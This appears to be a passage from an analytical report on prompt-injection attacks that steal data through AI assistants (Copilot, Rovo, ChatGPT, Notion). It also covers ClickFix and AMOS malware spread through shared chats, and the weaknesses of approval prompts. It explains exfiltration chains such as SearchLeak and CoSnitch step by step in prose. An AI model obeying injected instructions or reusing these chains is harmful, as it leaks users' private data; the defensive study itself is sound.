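The victim might have noticed Copilot working on a question they hadn't asked. Closing the tab would not have stopped the leak, because the session stayed active. Varonis reported the flaw in August 2025, and Microsoft patched it in January 2026. It never affected business customers. Taler does not say whether anyone had exploited it.

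### SearchLeak

The same kind of link later worked on Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise Search, which searches an employee's email, meetings and files. Taler (2026) writes in *SearchLeak* that this surprised the researchers, because the business product was supposed to have additional protections. Enterprise Search had no internet access of its own, so it could not send the data out as the consumer version had. The attack needed two more faults to get the data from Copilot's answer to the attacker's server.

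The first fault was that Enterprise Search took the search term from the web address and gave it to Copilot as a prompt. Copilot then treated the term as instructions as well as a query. A link could therefore contain instructions to find an email and put its subject line in the address of an image in Copilot's answer.

The second fault was a race condition, a fault in which the outcome depends on which of two events happens first. Microsoft had anticipated that answers might contain harmful HTML, the code that tells a browser what to put on a page. Copilot's software wrapped such code in a block that made the browser display it as plain text, but only once the answer was complete. Because Copilot shows its answers as it writes them, the browser briefly treated the unfinished answer as part of the page and requested an image it found there. By the time the block appeared, the browser had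 already sent out the image's address.

That request still had to get past Copilot's CSP, which would have blocked an image on the attacker's server. The third fault was that the policy allowed images from Bing, Microsoft's search engine. Bing can search for pictures similar to one the user supplies, and its servers fetch that picture from wherever it is hosted. Bing therefore passed the subject line on to the attacker's server, much as the Teams service had passed on data in EchoLeak. Engineers call this server-side request forgery, because an outsider gets a server to make a request for them.

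Taler argues that all three faults were necessary. Without the first, the attacker could not have put an image in Copilot's answer. Without the second, the browser would have displayed the image's code as text, and without the third, the CSP would have blocked the request. Race conditions and request forgery are old, well-known problems. Each fault might have looked minor to an engineer who reviewed it separately. For example, an image that loads too early does no harm if it can only come from Bing.

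SearchLeak depended on these faults, but other attacks have used substitutes for them. EchoLeak and the image attack in ReLeak delivered their instructions by email, so the employee did not have to click a link. SearchLeak required a click only because its instructions arrived in a link, so the click was a much weaker barrier than it appeared.

A stolen email subject line often contains a login code. An attacker who makes another service send such a code and then reads it may be able to take over the user's account on that service. According to The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox*, these codes often remain valid for several minutes. The attack could also reach meeting notes, salary information and anything else that the employee could open and Copilot had indexed.

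Before clicking, the employee could have seen a link to a genuine Microsoft domain, followed by a long string of encoded text. After the click, Copilot appeared to be working for a moment and perhaps gave an odd answer, but the data had already been sent. Taler advises users to check Microsoft 365 links for long, encoded additions. A specialist could do that, but most users would struggle because ordinary links to shared files are also long and unreadable.

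Microsoft registered the flaw as CVE-2026-42824 on June 4, 2026, and rated it critical, although it scored only medium on the standard severity scale. Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers and, according to The Next Web, found no evidence of malicious use.

### CoSnitch and RovoBlast

A simple precaution against entrance clicks is to fill in the prompt but wait for the user to press Enter, so the user can read it first. Consumer Copilot did this with ordinary links by the time of Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026), but an undocumented setting in the address made the prompt run as soon as the page loaded.

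The researchers learned about the setting by repeatedly asking Copilot why a prompt could not run by itself. In explaining why this was impossible, Copilot described the setting and the protections that were supposed to have disabled it, but these protections did not work.

Once the prompt was running, Copilot could search any services the user had connected, including Gmail, Google Drive and a calendar. In one test it retrieved an email with a password in plain text. It could then send data out with the tool it normally used to read web pages, so the request looked like any of its other web requests. As with Reprompt, the attack continued after the user closed the tab.

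Varonis advises people to read a prefilled prompt before it runs. This is sensible in general, but it would not have helped against CoSnitch, which gave the user no time to read the prompt. The user could have avoided the attack only by not clicking the link, which led to Copilot's real website.

Varonis told Microsoft about CoSnitch in December 2025, and Microsoft fixed it on August 18, 2026. TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions* lists the vulnerability as CVE-2026-24301, with a severity of 8.8 out of 10. Varonis saw no sign that anyone had exploited it during those eight months.

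The same research found that a web page could add instructions to Copilot's long-term memory if the user asked Copilot to summarize the page. The instructions stayed until the user deleted them in the settings, even after a password change. In one example, Copilot then described a known software flaw as harmless.

A click that opens an assistant can do similar damage without taking any data. Microsoft warns that some "Summarize with AI" buttons on websites also manipulate the assistant they open. In its fictional example, a finance chief clicks one of these buttons on a blog post and forgets about it. Weeks later, the assistant strongly recommends a particular supplier.

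Varonis' *RovoBlast* (2026) applied the attack to Rovo, an AI assistant from Atlassian, which makes the project tracker Jira and the internal documentation system Confluence. Rovo can search both, along with more than 50 other services that a customer may connect, such as Slack, Google Workspace and Microsoft 365. As with Copilot, a link could load a prompt into Rovo. The attacker did not need to know where the victim worked, because Atlassian filled in the user's default company identifier when none was given.

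Rovo also had a research agent that could browse the web through many steps without supervision. Following the attacker's instructions, Rovo collected internal material and the agent sent it to an outside site. SecurityWeek's *Critical One-Click Vulnerability in Atlassian’s Rovo AI Exposed Enterprise Data* lists three demonstrations in which the attack took Confluence pages, Jira tickets and SharePoint content that included personal data.

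Rovo gave no warning, asked for no confirmation and did not indicate that an outside link had started the session. Mascellino (2026), in *Researchers Uncover RovoBlast Vulnerability in Atlassian AI Assistant*, notes that the audit trail resembled ordinary research. An administrator reading it later would have had little more evidence of an attack than the employee did. Atlassian fixed the flaw before Varonis published its findings on August 7, and neither company mentioned a real attack.

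Atlassian's statement to SecurityWeek compared the attack to phishing and advised customers to check that content they give its apps comes from a trusted source. It also said the victim must "provide untrusted content" to Rovo, which is a strange way to describe clicking a link to Atlassian's own website. The employee may not have known that the link contained any content, and Atlassian's software accepted that content as a prompt.

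Varonis uses SearchLeak to argue that data can escape even when the assistant has no direct internet access. Willison's lethal trifecta already allows for this, but Varonis prefers to divide attacks into three stages, called Enter, Evade and Escape. These stages show how little the click that starts an attack reveals, because the user takes part only in Enter, before the assistant has accessed any private data.

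### ChatGPhish

Some links lead to a page where the attacker can ask the user for private data directly, and the links themselves contain neither that data nor instructions for an assistant. This is ordinary phishing, except that an assistant delivers the link. Permiso's *ChatGPhish* (May 2026) demonstrated this with ChatGPT's summaries of web pages.

The user opens a page in the Firefox browser and asks ChatGPT to summarise it. The page could be a company's website or a software project's documentation, with instructions that an attacker has added near the end. ChatGPT writes an accurate summary, then adds an alert about a new device on the user's account, with a link. The alert has the same formatting as the rest of the answer, and nothing marks the link as coming from the page. A user who believes the alert may click the link and type a password into the attacker's site.

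A check for private data in outgoing addresses would not catch this link, because the user supplies the data after clicking it. Permiso showed that the alert and link appeared, but did not test how many people would believe them or describe any real victims.

Permiso also made ChatGPT display a QR code instead of the link. A user who scans it moves from a computer to a phone and loses the protection of the browser's address preview, the employer's web filter and a password manager that might have detected the wrong domain.

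A user could have noticed that a summary is an odd place for a security alert, hovered over the link, or opened their account settings separately to look for the new device. Opening the settings separately works here, as it does against ordinary phishing, because the user doesn't have to judge the link.

OpenAI first told Permiso that it could not reproduce the problem. It marked a revised report as not applicable, then as a duplicate of an earlier one. eWeek's *‘ChatGPhish’ Attack Turns ChatGPT Summaries Into Phishing Lures* found no apparent fix at the end of May.

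### Why the usual advice fails

The link in an entrance click looks safe to people who check where it leads, as they have been told to do for years, because it really does lead to Microsoft or Atlassian. It also looks safe to filters that judge a link by its domain. The danger is in the text after the domain, which most people have never had a reason to read. Someone who does read it has to recognise an instruction to an AI system, which may be encoded and hard to tell apart from the long strings of characters in harmless links.

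Checking the domain is much better protection against an exit click, because the domain is usually the attacker's. But the user has to see the domain first, and an assistant can give a link any label. The address then stays hidden unless the user hovers over the link, which a phone has no pointer to do. The employee had little reason to look for an address behind Logue's button, and a QR code has no readable address until someone scans it.

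The advice to click only on links from trusted sources is even harder to apply, because the assistant appears to be the source. People learn to suspect unexpected messages, but the Slack developer had asked a question, and the link arrived as the answer, inside the company's own software and at a moment when an error message was plausible. Permiso calls this a transfer of trust, because text from a stranger's page gains the credibility of the assistant that repeats it. The assistant may also write more fluently than the attacker would have, which removes the clumsy wording that often helps people spot a scam.

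Varonis also tells users to close the session and report it if an assistant behaves strangely. Reporting it may help a security team find out what happened, but closing the tab did not stop the leak in Reprompt or CoSnitch, and in SearchLeak the strange behaviour was visible only as the data left.

eWeek offers a stricter rule, which is to distrust any link, image or QR code in an AI summary unless the user can verify its source. Someone who followed it consistently would avoid most exit clicks, as well as ChatGPhish. They would also have to go back to the original pages and messages to check, and people ask for a summary largely to avoid reading those.

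## Commands that the user copies, and what real attackers have done

A copied command can expose more data than a link, which can leak only what the model has put in its address from the conversation or from something else the assistant could read. If a user copies a line of code from an answer and pastes it into a terminal, a window for typing instructions to the operating system, the computer runs it with the user's permissions. The code can open any file that the user can open, including saved passwords and documents that the assistant never saw. It can also download a larger program that keeps running after the user has closed the chat.

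The controls on the assistant don't apply once the user runs a copied command. Content security policies and link checks cover what the assistant displays, but a program in a terminal makes its own connections. The operating system may not block the command either. On Macs, Gatekeeper checks downloaded apps before they open, but as Huntress' *AMOS Stealer Exploits AI Trust* points out, it does not inspect commands that people paste into the terminal.

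A pasted command can also make a very limited assistant dangerous. Of the three features in Willison's lethal trifecta, the assistant needs only exposure to untrusted content, because the user's computer supplies the private data and the network connection. Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Uncover 10 In-the-Wild Prompt Injection Payloads Targeting AI Agents* quotes Mayur Sewani, a researcher at the security company Forcepoint: "A browser AI that can only summarize is low-risk." That is right about what the AI can do by itself, but it doesn't account for a user who follows the summary's advice.

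### ClickFix

Criminals already use an established technique, which security researchers call ClickFix, to get people to paste commands. A web page displays a fake problem, such as a failed test to prove that the visitor is human, and gives steps to fix it. One step is to paste a command that installs malicious software. Because the visitor installs the software, defences that scan downloaded files and email attachments may have nothing to examine.

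ClickFix doesn't need an AI assistant, and it is one of the most common ways for criminals to get into an organisation's computers. The Hacker News' *17,000 URLs Reveal How ClickFix Turns Trusted Websites Into Malware Traps* (2026) reports that ClickFix accounted for 47% of the initial-access cases (the intruder's first way in) that Microsoft's Defender Experts handled in 2025. SecurityBrief UK gives a much lower figure, 14.9% of initial access activity in incidents between March and May 2026, although ClickFix was still the dominant delivery technique in that period. Beazley Security's *Quarterly Threat Report* (2026) found that 19% of ransomware cases in the third quarter began with malware, mostly ClickFix, which would put ClickFix's own share of those ransomware cases between a tenth and a fifth.

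These companies count different customers and different kinds of incident, so their figures do not show that ClickFix declined after 2025. *ClickFix Now Cybercriminals' Favorite Malware Delivery Technique* (Palmer, 2026) instead reports that the security company ReliaQuest saw a surge in ClickFix attacks on both Windows and Mac users. Microsoft (2026) lists ClickFix with phishing and impersonation among the ways attackers still heavily exploit people.

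### A summary that passes on the instructions

In 2025 the security company CloudSEK showed that an AI summary can relay a ClickFix attack. Its researchers made a web page with visible text about nerve signals and the immune system. Hidden text on the page repeated the steps for a fake repair many times and instructed any AI summariser to present only those steps. The researchers used a harmless command in the steps.

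The researchers ran the page through Sider.ai, a commercial AI tool, and through a summarising browser extension they had built. Both produced summaries with instructions to paste and run the command. Most of the summaries contained only these instructions, but a few also mentioned the nerve signals, which might have made a reader wonder what the repair had to do with the article.

CloudSEK did not report how many times it ran the test, and it named only these two tools. It predicted that better wording would bring the success rate close to 100%. Nobody outside the research team had to decide whether to follow the steps. Someone who has asked for a summary of a medical article has little reason to expect instructions for repairing a computer, and many people would probably not have followed them.

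CloudSEK recommends that summarisers remove text a human reader could not see, look for typical attack commands and show whether an instruction came from a hidden part of the page, which users cannot tell from the summary alone. It also warned that criminals could adopt the technique within weeks. The attacks that came to light in December 2025 were simpler than this technique.

### Shared conversations

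On December 5, 2025, the security company Huntress investigated an alert about Atomic macOS Stealer, or AMOS, a program that steals data from Macs. Its makers run a large criminal business, supplying AMOS to other criminals as a service. *Why AMOS matters*, from the security company Sophos, reports that AMOS accounted for almost 40% of the Mac protection updates Sophos issued in 2025.

Huntress found that the user had searched Google for a way to clear disk space and clicked a result near the top, which led to a conversation on ChatGPT's real website. Huntress had expected to find a phishing email, a fake installer or a ClickFix page.

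ChatGPT and xAI's chatbot Grok both let people publish a conversation at its own web address. An attacker had created and shared a ChatGPT conversation that read as a guide to freeing up space on a Mac. The guide had numbered steps, assurances that it would not touch personal data, and a command, which the user ran.

The command downloaded a script that asked for the Mac's password, checked that it was correct and used it to take full control of the computer. AMOS collects passwords saved in browsers, the Mac's keychain (where the system stores passwords and certificates), cryptocurrency wallets and sensitive documents, and sends them to the attacker's server. If it finds either of two popular cryptocurrency apps, it replaces the app with a fake that asks the owner to re-enter the wallet's recovery phrase. It also runs again each time the computer starts.

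Unlike EchoLeak and SearchLeak, this attack had a real victim. Huntress did not estimate how many other victims there were, but it found the same kind of result in several similar searches and a nearly identical guide on Grok. Huntress thought the attackers had manipulated Google's search rankings, whereas Malwarebytes' *Google ads funnel Mac users to poisoned AI chats* (2025) attributes the traffic to advertisements. The difference matters for prevention because Google can review an advertisement before running it.

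Kaspersky (2025) reported a similar campaign on December 15. The attackers bought advertisements on searches for Atlas, OpenAI's web browser. The advertisements led to a shared ChatGPT conversation that looked like an installation guide for Atlas, but the command in the guide installed AMOS. Kaspersky's *Infostealer has entered the chat* (2025) explains that the attackers had prompted ChatGPT to write the guide and then removed the earlier part of the conversation. In this campaign, AMOS took text files, PDFs and Word documents from the usual folders, along with passwords and browser data. It also installed a backdoor that let the attackers control the Mac remotely.

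A notice above the guide identified it as a copy of a conversation between ChatGPT and an anonymous user. Kaspersky thinks a careful reader would have understood from this that the page was not official, but a reader who understood the notice could still have trusted the guide because ChatGPT had written it. The notice did not include what the user had asked for.

Kaspersky calls this a variation of ClickFix because the user runs a command that downloads malicious software. Huntress says its own case was not ClickFix, a term it associates with fake tests to prove a visitor is human. Two companies could therefore count the same theft differently, which is another reason to compare their ClickFix percentages cautiously.

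The usual advice would not have helped much, because the address belonged to ChatGPT and the user had been looking for technical instructions, so a command seemed plausible. Huntress advises users to be suspicious of any tool that asks for a password if they don't fully understand what the tool does. The request for the Mac's password was probably the best remaining clue, since it did not come from a normal macOS password window, but the user had already run the first command by then.

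### Injected instructions and published ones

In the December campaigns, the attackers had ChatGPT write the guides and published them on a trusted site, where the victims later read them. The attackers did not trick the victims' own assistants, and ChatGPT had no access to the victims' files. Training a model to ignore instructions in documents would have made no difference, because the attackers wrote their prompts as ordinary users.

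OpenAI and xAI could reduce this risk by checking shared conversations for commands that download software. In CloudSEK's experiment, the user's own assistant read a hostile page and repeated what was hidden in it, so the remedy was to clean up the page before it reached the model. Neither Huntress nor Kaspersky found criminals using hidden instructions to make a victim's assistant recommend a command. Criminals have put malicious commands in AI-written text, but so far only researchers are known to have used an injection to put them in a summary.

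Kaspersky suggests pasting an unfamiliar command into a chatbot and asking whether it is safe. When its researchers asked ChatGPT about the fake Atlas instructions, it warned against following them. Kaspersky's advice is good for someone reading a shared conversation, but a user whose own assistant produced the command should ask in a new chat, without the page or email that the assistant was reading. The attacker's instructions are still in the old chat's context and may influence the second opinion as well, much as happened when the journalist in the Bing Chat test asked about a suspicious link.

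### Injections on the public web

If criminals were using prompt injection widely, some of it should be visible on public websites. In *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (April 2026), Khodayari, Acharya and Zhang searched for 3,963 phrases typical of injections at 1.2 billion web addresses from about half of the October 2025 edition of Common Crawl, a public archive of web pages. They added results from Censys and Shodan, two search engines for internet-connected servers.

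The search produced 31,206 matches, many of them in tutorials and articles about prompt injection. Two reviewers sorted the matches using software that grouped similar ones, and confirmed 15,387 injections on 11,722 pages. In Common Crawl alone, they found injections on 9,676 pages, or about eight in every million. They then labeled the injections by purpose, sometimes giving one more than one label.

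| Apparent purpose | Injections |
|---|---|
| Disrupt the AI system, usually by making it produce nonsense | 8,894 |
| Stop AI systems from reusing personal or copyrighted material | 4,093 |
| Reveal whether a visitor is an AI | 3,096 |
| Override the AI's task for no clear reason | 2,632 |
| Promote a product, website or person | 1,521 |
| Obtain data | 13 |

Thirteen of the injections, fewer than one in a thousand, were designed to extract data. Nine targeted the system prompt, the developer's standing instructions to the model, which usually contains nothing about the user. The other four targeted secrets. Website operators placed more than three quarters of all the injections on their own sites, and many of these operators were trying to keep AI systems away from their content.

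Khodayari and colleagues also tested how well the injections worked. They chose 100 and had 13 models summarise the page containing each one in four formats, for a total of 5,200 runs. The models followed the injection 3.9% of the time when they received the page as plain text, and 1.1% of the time when they received its HTML. Small models reading plain text had the highest rate, at 8%, while closed-source models such as OpenAI's followed the injection in only five of 800 runs across all formats. In six cases, a model recognised the injection but still followed it.

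HTML shows which text is hidden, but converting the page to plain text can remove that clue and keep the hidden words. CloudSEK blamed summarisers that read raw HTML, but a developer who strips out the formatting and leaves the hidden text may increase the risk. Some models could not handle the longer HTML pages and failed in about a fifth of those runs. Those failures explain only a little of the gap between the formats, because the rate among completed runs would still be about 1.4%.

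These success rates are weak evidence about data theft, because almost none of the injections were designed to steal anything. The models also only wrote summaries and had no tools or private files that an attacker could use.

Google searched several monthly editions of Common Crawl, each with two to three billion pages, for phrases typical of prompt injections. Its researchers used Google's Gemini model to judge the intent of each match, then reviewed the results by hand. They reported a "small number" of injections aimed at stealing data but gave no count. The example they published appeared to be a website author's experiment. They did not see significant use of the exfiltration prompts that security researchers had published in 2025, and concluded that attackers had not yet used that research at scale.

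Google also found 32% more malicious injections in February 2026 than in November 2025. That category included attempts to delete files as well as to steal data. Without the counts, it is hard to tell whether the increase was a handful of pages or many more.

Unit 42's *Fooling AI Agents*, published in March 2026, is more alarming. Unit 42 is the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, and the paper draws on web traffic that the company monitors. It concludes that attackers are actively using prompt injection, and describes websites that try to make AI agents approve a fraudulent advertisement, buy running shoes or send $5,000 to a stranger. A line in the footer of one personal website sought private information, asking for contact details from the AI user's company.

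Unit 42 gives that footer its highest severity rating, critical. The rating reflects the harm a successful injection would cause, because the team has limited visibility into which techniques succeed. The team knew of no confirmed case in which the advertisement attack had worked against a real reviewing system. Its cases are good evidence that people are trying these attacks, but much weaker evidence that anyone has lost data to them.

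Other security companies have found a few more serious attempts. Forcepoint's ten examples, which Infosecurity Magazine reported in April 2026, included at least one that tried to steal API keys. Infosecurity Magazine's *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* describes two campaigns that Zscaler discovered. One ran a payment scam through fake software documentation, and the other impersonated a cryptocurrency service. In both, the attackers pushed their pages up the search rankings so that AI agents would find them. Criminals who can get an agent to pay them directly may have little interest in stealing its user's email.

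All of these surveys looked at web content, where they were unlikely to find the attacks that worked best in researchers' demonstrations. EchoLeak and ReLeak began with a private email, and SearchLeak and CoSnitch began with a link that an attacker could send to one person. Khodayari and colleagues note that even on the web, Common Crawl omits pages behind a login, a hostile site can show its injection only to AI agents, and a search for known phrases misses subtler wording, so they treat their count as a minimum.

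### What "no known exploitation" means

The main evidence about real attacks through email and links comes from the companies involved. Microsoft knew of none that used EchoLeak or SearchLeak, Varonis knew of none that used CoSnitch, and Cato knew of none that used ReLeak.

An announcement that an investigation found no attacks is more reassuring if the investigation was likely to detect them. Suppose, for illustration, that there was a 20% chance somebody had exploited a flaw before anyone looked. If the investigation would have caught nine out of ten attacks, finding nothing lowers that chance to about 2%. If it would have caught only one in ten, the chance is still about 18%.

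An employer would have had trouble detecting most of these attacks. In EchoLeak and SearchLeak, the employee's browser requested an image from a Microsoft server, so the employer's network records would show a connection to a permitted domain, which is routine in an office that uses Microsoft's software. In ReLeak's document attack, Microsoft's servers made the request, so the employer's network would have had no record of it.

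Microsoft was in a better position because it runs the Teams and Bing services that passed the requests on, so it could have looked for image requests that ended at unfamiliar servers. The original attack might also have left traces. An injected email stays in the mailbox until somebody deletes it, and SearchLeak's instructions were part of a web address, which servers commonly log. If these records went back far enough, a thorough search of them would make Microsoft's statements fairly strong evidence. But Microsoft has a commercial interest in finding nothing, and outsiders can't repeat the search.

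Varonis and Cato do not run Copilot, so their statements are weaker evidence on this point. They could know only about attacks they had seen or heard about, a much smaller set than all the attacks that might have happened.

Claims that attackers have exploited a flaw also need checking. OECD's *Critical SearchLeak Vulnerability in Microsoft 365 Copilot Exposes Sensitive Data*, an entry in a public database of AI incidents, classifies SearchLeak as an actual incident on the grounds that Microsoft patched it "after being exploited". An AI wrote that explanation, which includes no evidence of an attack. The AI may have mistaken the researchers' demonstration for a real theft. A count of incidents based on the database would therefore include one with no identified victim.

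Pasted commands are much easier to detect afterwards than image requests. AMOS leaves programs and files on the victim's computer, and Huntress discovered the December attack because security software raised an alert. An image request leaves nothing comparable on the computer. This difference may partly explain why the known victims are mostly people who pasted commands.

Even so, ordinary criminals probably do prefer pasted commands. The EchoLeak team spent about three months studying Copilot, and Microsoft could stop the attack with a fix on its own servers. ClickFix needs no flaw in any particular product, and it can yield every password on a computer. Google makes a similar argument about effort and reward, but expects the balance to change as AI systems become more valuable targets and attackers automate more of their work. A spy who wants one executive's correspondence, rather than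 thousands of passwords, might consider three months of work worthwhile for an attack that leaves so few traces.

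## What approval prompts check and what they miss

People who click a link or paste a command often don't realise they are making a security decision. An approval prompt at least makes the decision visible, because the assistant stops and waits for an answer.

Suppose an office worker asks an AI assistant to reply to a supplier. The model can't send the email itself, so it writes a request in a fixed format that names a tool and its inputs, which here are the recipient, subject and text. The software around the model holds the request and shows the worker a dialog describing it. If the worker agrees, the software runs the tool, which sends the email.

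Larger organisations may separate these jobs further. AWS, Amazon's cloud computing business, documents a design in which an automated workflow pauses and issues a token that identifies the paused step. A separate application asks a reviewer to decide and returns the token with a yes or no. The application holds the credentials needed to answer, so a model without access to the application can't approve its own request.

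For the decision to protect anyone's data, four conditions have to hold:

1. The description matches the action that will run.
2. The user can judge from the description whether the action is harmful.
3. The question comes before the action has any effect.
4. Every route by which data could leave leads to a question, unless something else blocks it.

A prompt that meets three of these can still let all the data out.

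### Matching the description to the action

Many coding agents write the text of their own approval dialogs. Weng (2026), in *What You Approve Is What Executes*, objects that the user then approves a summary written by the component that a prompt injection may have taken over. Researchers have shown that an attacker who controls an agent can make its dialogs misdescribe an action. According to Weng, the vendors who heard about this considered it outside their threat models.

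Banks have dealt with a similar problem. *Approve What, Exactly?* (Kodathala, Pollishetty and Cargill, 2026) points to European payment rules, which tie the code that authorises a remote payment to the amount and the payee. The payer has to see both, and changing either invalidates the code.

Weng proposes a comparable design for agents, in which a program outside the agent, which Weng calls a mediator, intercepts each action, works out what the action would do and writes the approval dialog. The agent's own explanation appears only as untrusted text. The approval covers that exact action, so the mediator refuses to run anything the agent substitutes afterwards.

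A payment is easy to describe, but a command may start a script that starts another program, and no software can work out in advance what every program will do. Weng's mediator labels whatever it can't analyse "uninspectable". It prompts the user about these cases and about actions it recognises as dangerous, and lets the rest through.

Weng tested a prototype on two public collections of commands. The first contained 1,330 ways to misuse ordinary Unix programs. The prototype let 10.0% of them through without a prompt. It named a specific danger in 405 of the others and labelled the remaining 792 uninspectable. The second contained 28,798 examples of normal use. The prototype let only 4.1% of these through without a prompt and labelled 87.0% uninspectable.

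Both kinds of error depend on the mediator's list of trusted programs. Every misuse it missed ran through a program on the list, and most of the normal commands it labeled uninspectable got that label because their program wasn't on the list. A longer list would reduce the prompts but let more misuse through. Better analysis helps somewhat, and one round of improvements had already cut missed misuse from 15.0% to 10.0%. Weng doubts that a mediator can avoid the trade-off if it examines actions only as they leave the agent.

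The label is also a poor warning, because it appeared on 60% of the harmful commands and 87% of the normal ones. A user who saw it would have no reason to think a command was dangerous. Daily work would probably produce fewer prompts than the test did, because the collection includes many rarely used programs and most people use a small set of programs repeatedly. The programs people use most are also the most likely to be on a trust list, where the prototype's misses occurred.

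Weng's prototype doesn't implement two parts of the design. It doesn't intercept every action on a computer, so an agent could act without going through the mediator. It also doesn't protect the dialog from an agent that tries to draw over it or answer it.

Kodathala and colleagues address an easier problem, in which the agent can use only tools with defined inputs, such as tools for sending email or making payments. A gateway on a separate machine builds an approval card from those inputs. Once the user approves the card on a phone, the gateway runs the request it stored.

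Some products already use a language model instead of a person to approve requests. In one test, 15 models acting as approvers reviewed 23 harmful and 11 harmless requests. They caught 30% of the harmful requests when they read the agent's description and 98% when they read the card. One harmful request was to send an email to both the user's boss and an outside address. All 15 models approved it when they read the agent's description and refused it when they read the card, which listed both recipients.

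The models also refused 16% of the harmless requests when shown the card, but none when shown the description. Placeholder text in the researchers' test messages caused most of these refusals, and without those refusals the rate would have been about 2%. Kodathala and colleagues tested no human approvers. A model reads the whole card every time, which is a lot to expect of an employee, so 98% is probably too optimistic for people.

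Few of the tools for building agents come with this protection. The same researchers audited ten of them. For eight approval mechanisms, they could measure whether the action that ran was always the one the user had approved. Three passed, one passed in part, and four allowed the action to change after approval. Developers also had to design the dialogs themselves. The audit left out commercial coding agents such as Claude Code and Cursor, which may do better or worse.

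### Giving the user enough to judge

Weng's mediator guarantees an accurate description but leaves open whether people understand it. An accurate description can also omit the one detail that matters.

Under tool-level approval, an agent asks for permission to use a whole tool, and users routinely grant it without seeing what the tool will send. Zhang and Pei (2026) explain in *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* that a user who approves a web search tool gives the agent the entire capability without seeing the addresses or search terms it will use. Under request-level approval, the software asks about each use and shows what the tool is about to send.

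Tool-level approval can help a user decide whether to trust the company that made the tool. It can't detect a leak, because the same tool can send both harmless requests and requests containing a password. Zhang and Pei add that agent interfaces typically cut off the end of long addresses, which is usually where the stolen data is. They base this on industry publications and did not survey products themselves.

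The Model Context Protocol, a widely used standard for connecting AI models to outside tools, recommends showing the user a tool's inputs before sending them to the tool's server, "to avoid malicious or accidental data exfiltration". Because the standard uses "should", an app can hide the inputs and still comply.

App makers have a reason to hide approval prompts. A research task may need dozens of searches, and few people would read dozens of dialogs carefully. Kodathala and colleagues were able to test seven development tools for a limit on how many approval requests an agent could make, and none had one. In five of the seven, a single model turn produced 20 requests waiting for an answer.

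Showing less on each dialog saves reading time but removes evidence. In a simulation by the same researchers, the approver let through 20% of attacks when the dialog showed only the payee and the amount, compared with 6% when it showed the full card. The shorter dialog left out details such as the text of an email and any extra recipient. The simulated approver was a program with assumed error rates, so these figures illustrate the problem but don't measure how people behave. Data theft is often visible only in the missing details. For example, an email can go to the right supplier with the wrong attachment.

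People may also check more carefully when they have something concrete to inspect. Wu, Wermke and colleagues (2026), in *From Delegation to Action Approval*, surveyed 203 developers who use coding agents. Those who inspected diffs, which show which lines of a file have changed, were less likely to approve certain sensitive actions, including access to passwords and personal data, without close review. Careful people may do both, so the survey can't show that diffs cause the extra care.

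One developer in the survey wanted an agent to "clearly explain what it changed before asking me to approve it". That would help when the agent is working properly, but if an injection has taken it over, the explanation is part of the attack. Kodathala and colleagues simulated an approver who believed the agent's explanation whenever it appeared. Attacks on this approver succeeded 54% of the time with or without the accurate card, and the rate fell to 5% only when the researchers removed the agent's explanation from the card. The 15 language models weren't misled this way. Nobody has tested whether people would be, so it seems prudent to hide the explanation until the user asks for it, as the researchers' card does.

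### Asking before anything happens

The approval prompt in Notion, an app for shared documents, was accurate and detailed but came too late. PromptArmor's *Notion AI*, published in January 2026, describes a user who uploads a job applicant's CV containing hidden instructions and asks the assistant to update a hiring tracker. The assistant inserts an image into the tracker and puts the tracker's text in the image's address.

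Notion then prompted the user to say whether they trusted the outside site. The warning displayed the address, including data from the tracker, so an attentive user could have recognised the theft. But Notion had already saved the edit and the user's browser had requested the image, so the attacker received the data whether or not the user accepted the edit. The data included salary expectations, feedback on candidates and internal details about the job.

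Refusing might even have made things worse, because a user who clicked "no" would reasonably believe they had stopped the leak and have little reason to report it.

PromptArmor reported the flaw on December 24, 2025, through HackerOne, a company that receives vulnerability reports for other organizations. Five days later the report was closed as "not applicable", apparently before anyone at Notion had seen it. PromptArmor went public on January 7. Notion contacted PromptArmor that day and repaired the document edits by night. PromptArmor describes a demonstration and mentions no victims.

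Notion had added an approval step a few months earlier. The Decoder's *Notion AI agents get security update after data leak* (2025) reports that, after researchers demonstrated a different leak in September, users had to approve any suspicious or model-generated link before an agent opened it. In the hiring tracker case, the agent edited a document rather than opening a link, and the user's browser then sent the data out.

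PromptArmor also found that the assistant in Notion's email app could put outside images in a draft. Users are supposed to be able to review a draft safely before deciding whether to send it, but if the draft loads outside images, data can leave while they are still reading. The software therefore must not fetch anything from outside to display a proposed edit or message before the user approves it. PromptArmor recommended that Notion stop loading outside images automatically in both places.

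### Covering every route

Chat apps usually load images and link previews without asking the user, and a prompt before every image would be disruptive. The Model Context Protocol's advice about showing inputs doesn't help here because it applies to tool calls, and loading an image in an answer isn't one.

Tools can also be exempt from approval. *The Hitchhiker's Guide to Agentic AI* (2026) recommends that agents always ask before irreversible actions, such as deleting files, sending emails and making purchases. It classes reading files and searching the web as reversible, so they generally need no approval. This rule is good for preventing accidental damage, but it fails to protect private data because a search sends its terms to someone else's server, and nobody can take them back. An agent that follows the rule could read a confidential file and send parts of it out as search terms without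 prompting the user for approval.

Some software makes such exemptions automatically. The Model Context Protocol (2026) blog explains that toolmakers can label their tools read-only, and an app that trusts the maker might then approve the tool without asking the user. A tool that fetches web pages may fit the label because it doesn't change the pages, but it can still send data out in the web addresses it requests.

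The same blog post discusses labels that would address this directly by recording whether a tool reads private data, handles untrusted content or can send data out, the three parts of Willison's lethal trifecta. Once an agent had read something untrusted, the software could block any tool that can send data or ask the user first. Several proposals to define such labels are open. The labels would spare users a prompt for every harmless search, but they would rarely help with an email assistant, which reads untrusted content all day.

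Kodathala and colleagues replayed 609 combinations of an ordinary task and an injected one, with an agent that lied about what it was doing and a simulated approver that compared each card perfectly with the user's task. The accurate card reduced the attacks' success rate from 54% to 3%. The attacks that still succeeded all used actions that the gateway's policy exempted from approval, such as fetching a web page. The 3% figure is small, but fetching a page is one of the main ways for data to leave, and a better card would not prevent it.

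The obvious response is to ask users to approve more actions. Notion has a setting that requires confirmation for web requests, and PromptArmor advises users to turn it on. OpenAI asks for approval only when its software can't establish that an address is safe, which should mean far fewer prompts.

### What the official guidance asks for

Security organisations and AI companies widely recommend human approval, but they are more specific about when to ask than about what to show.

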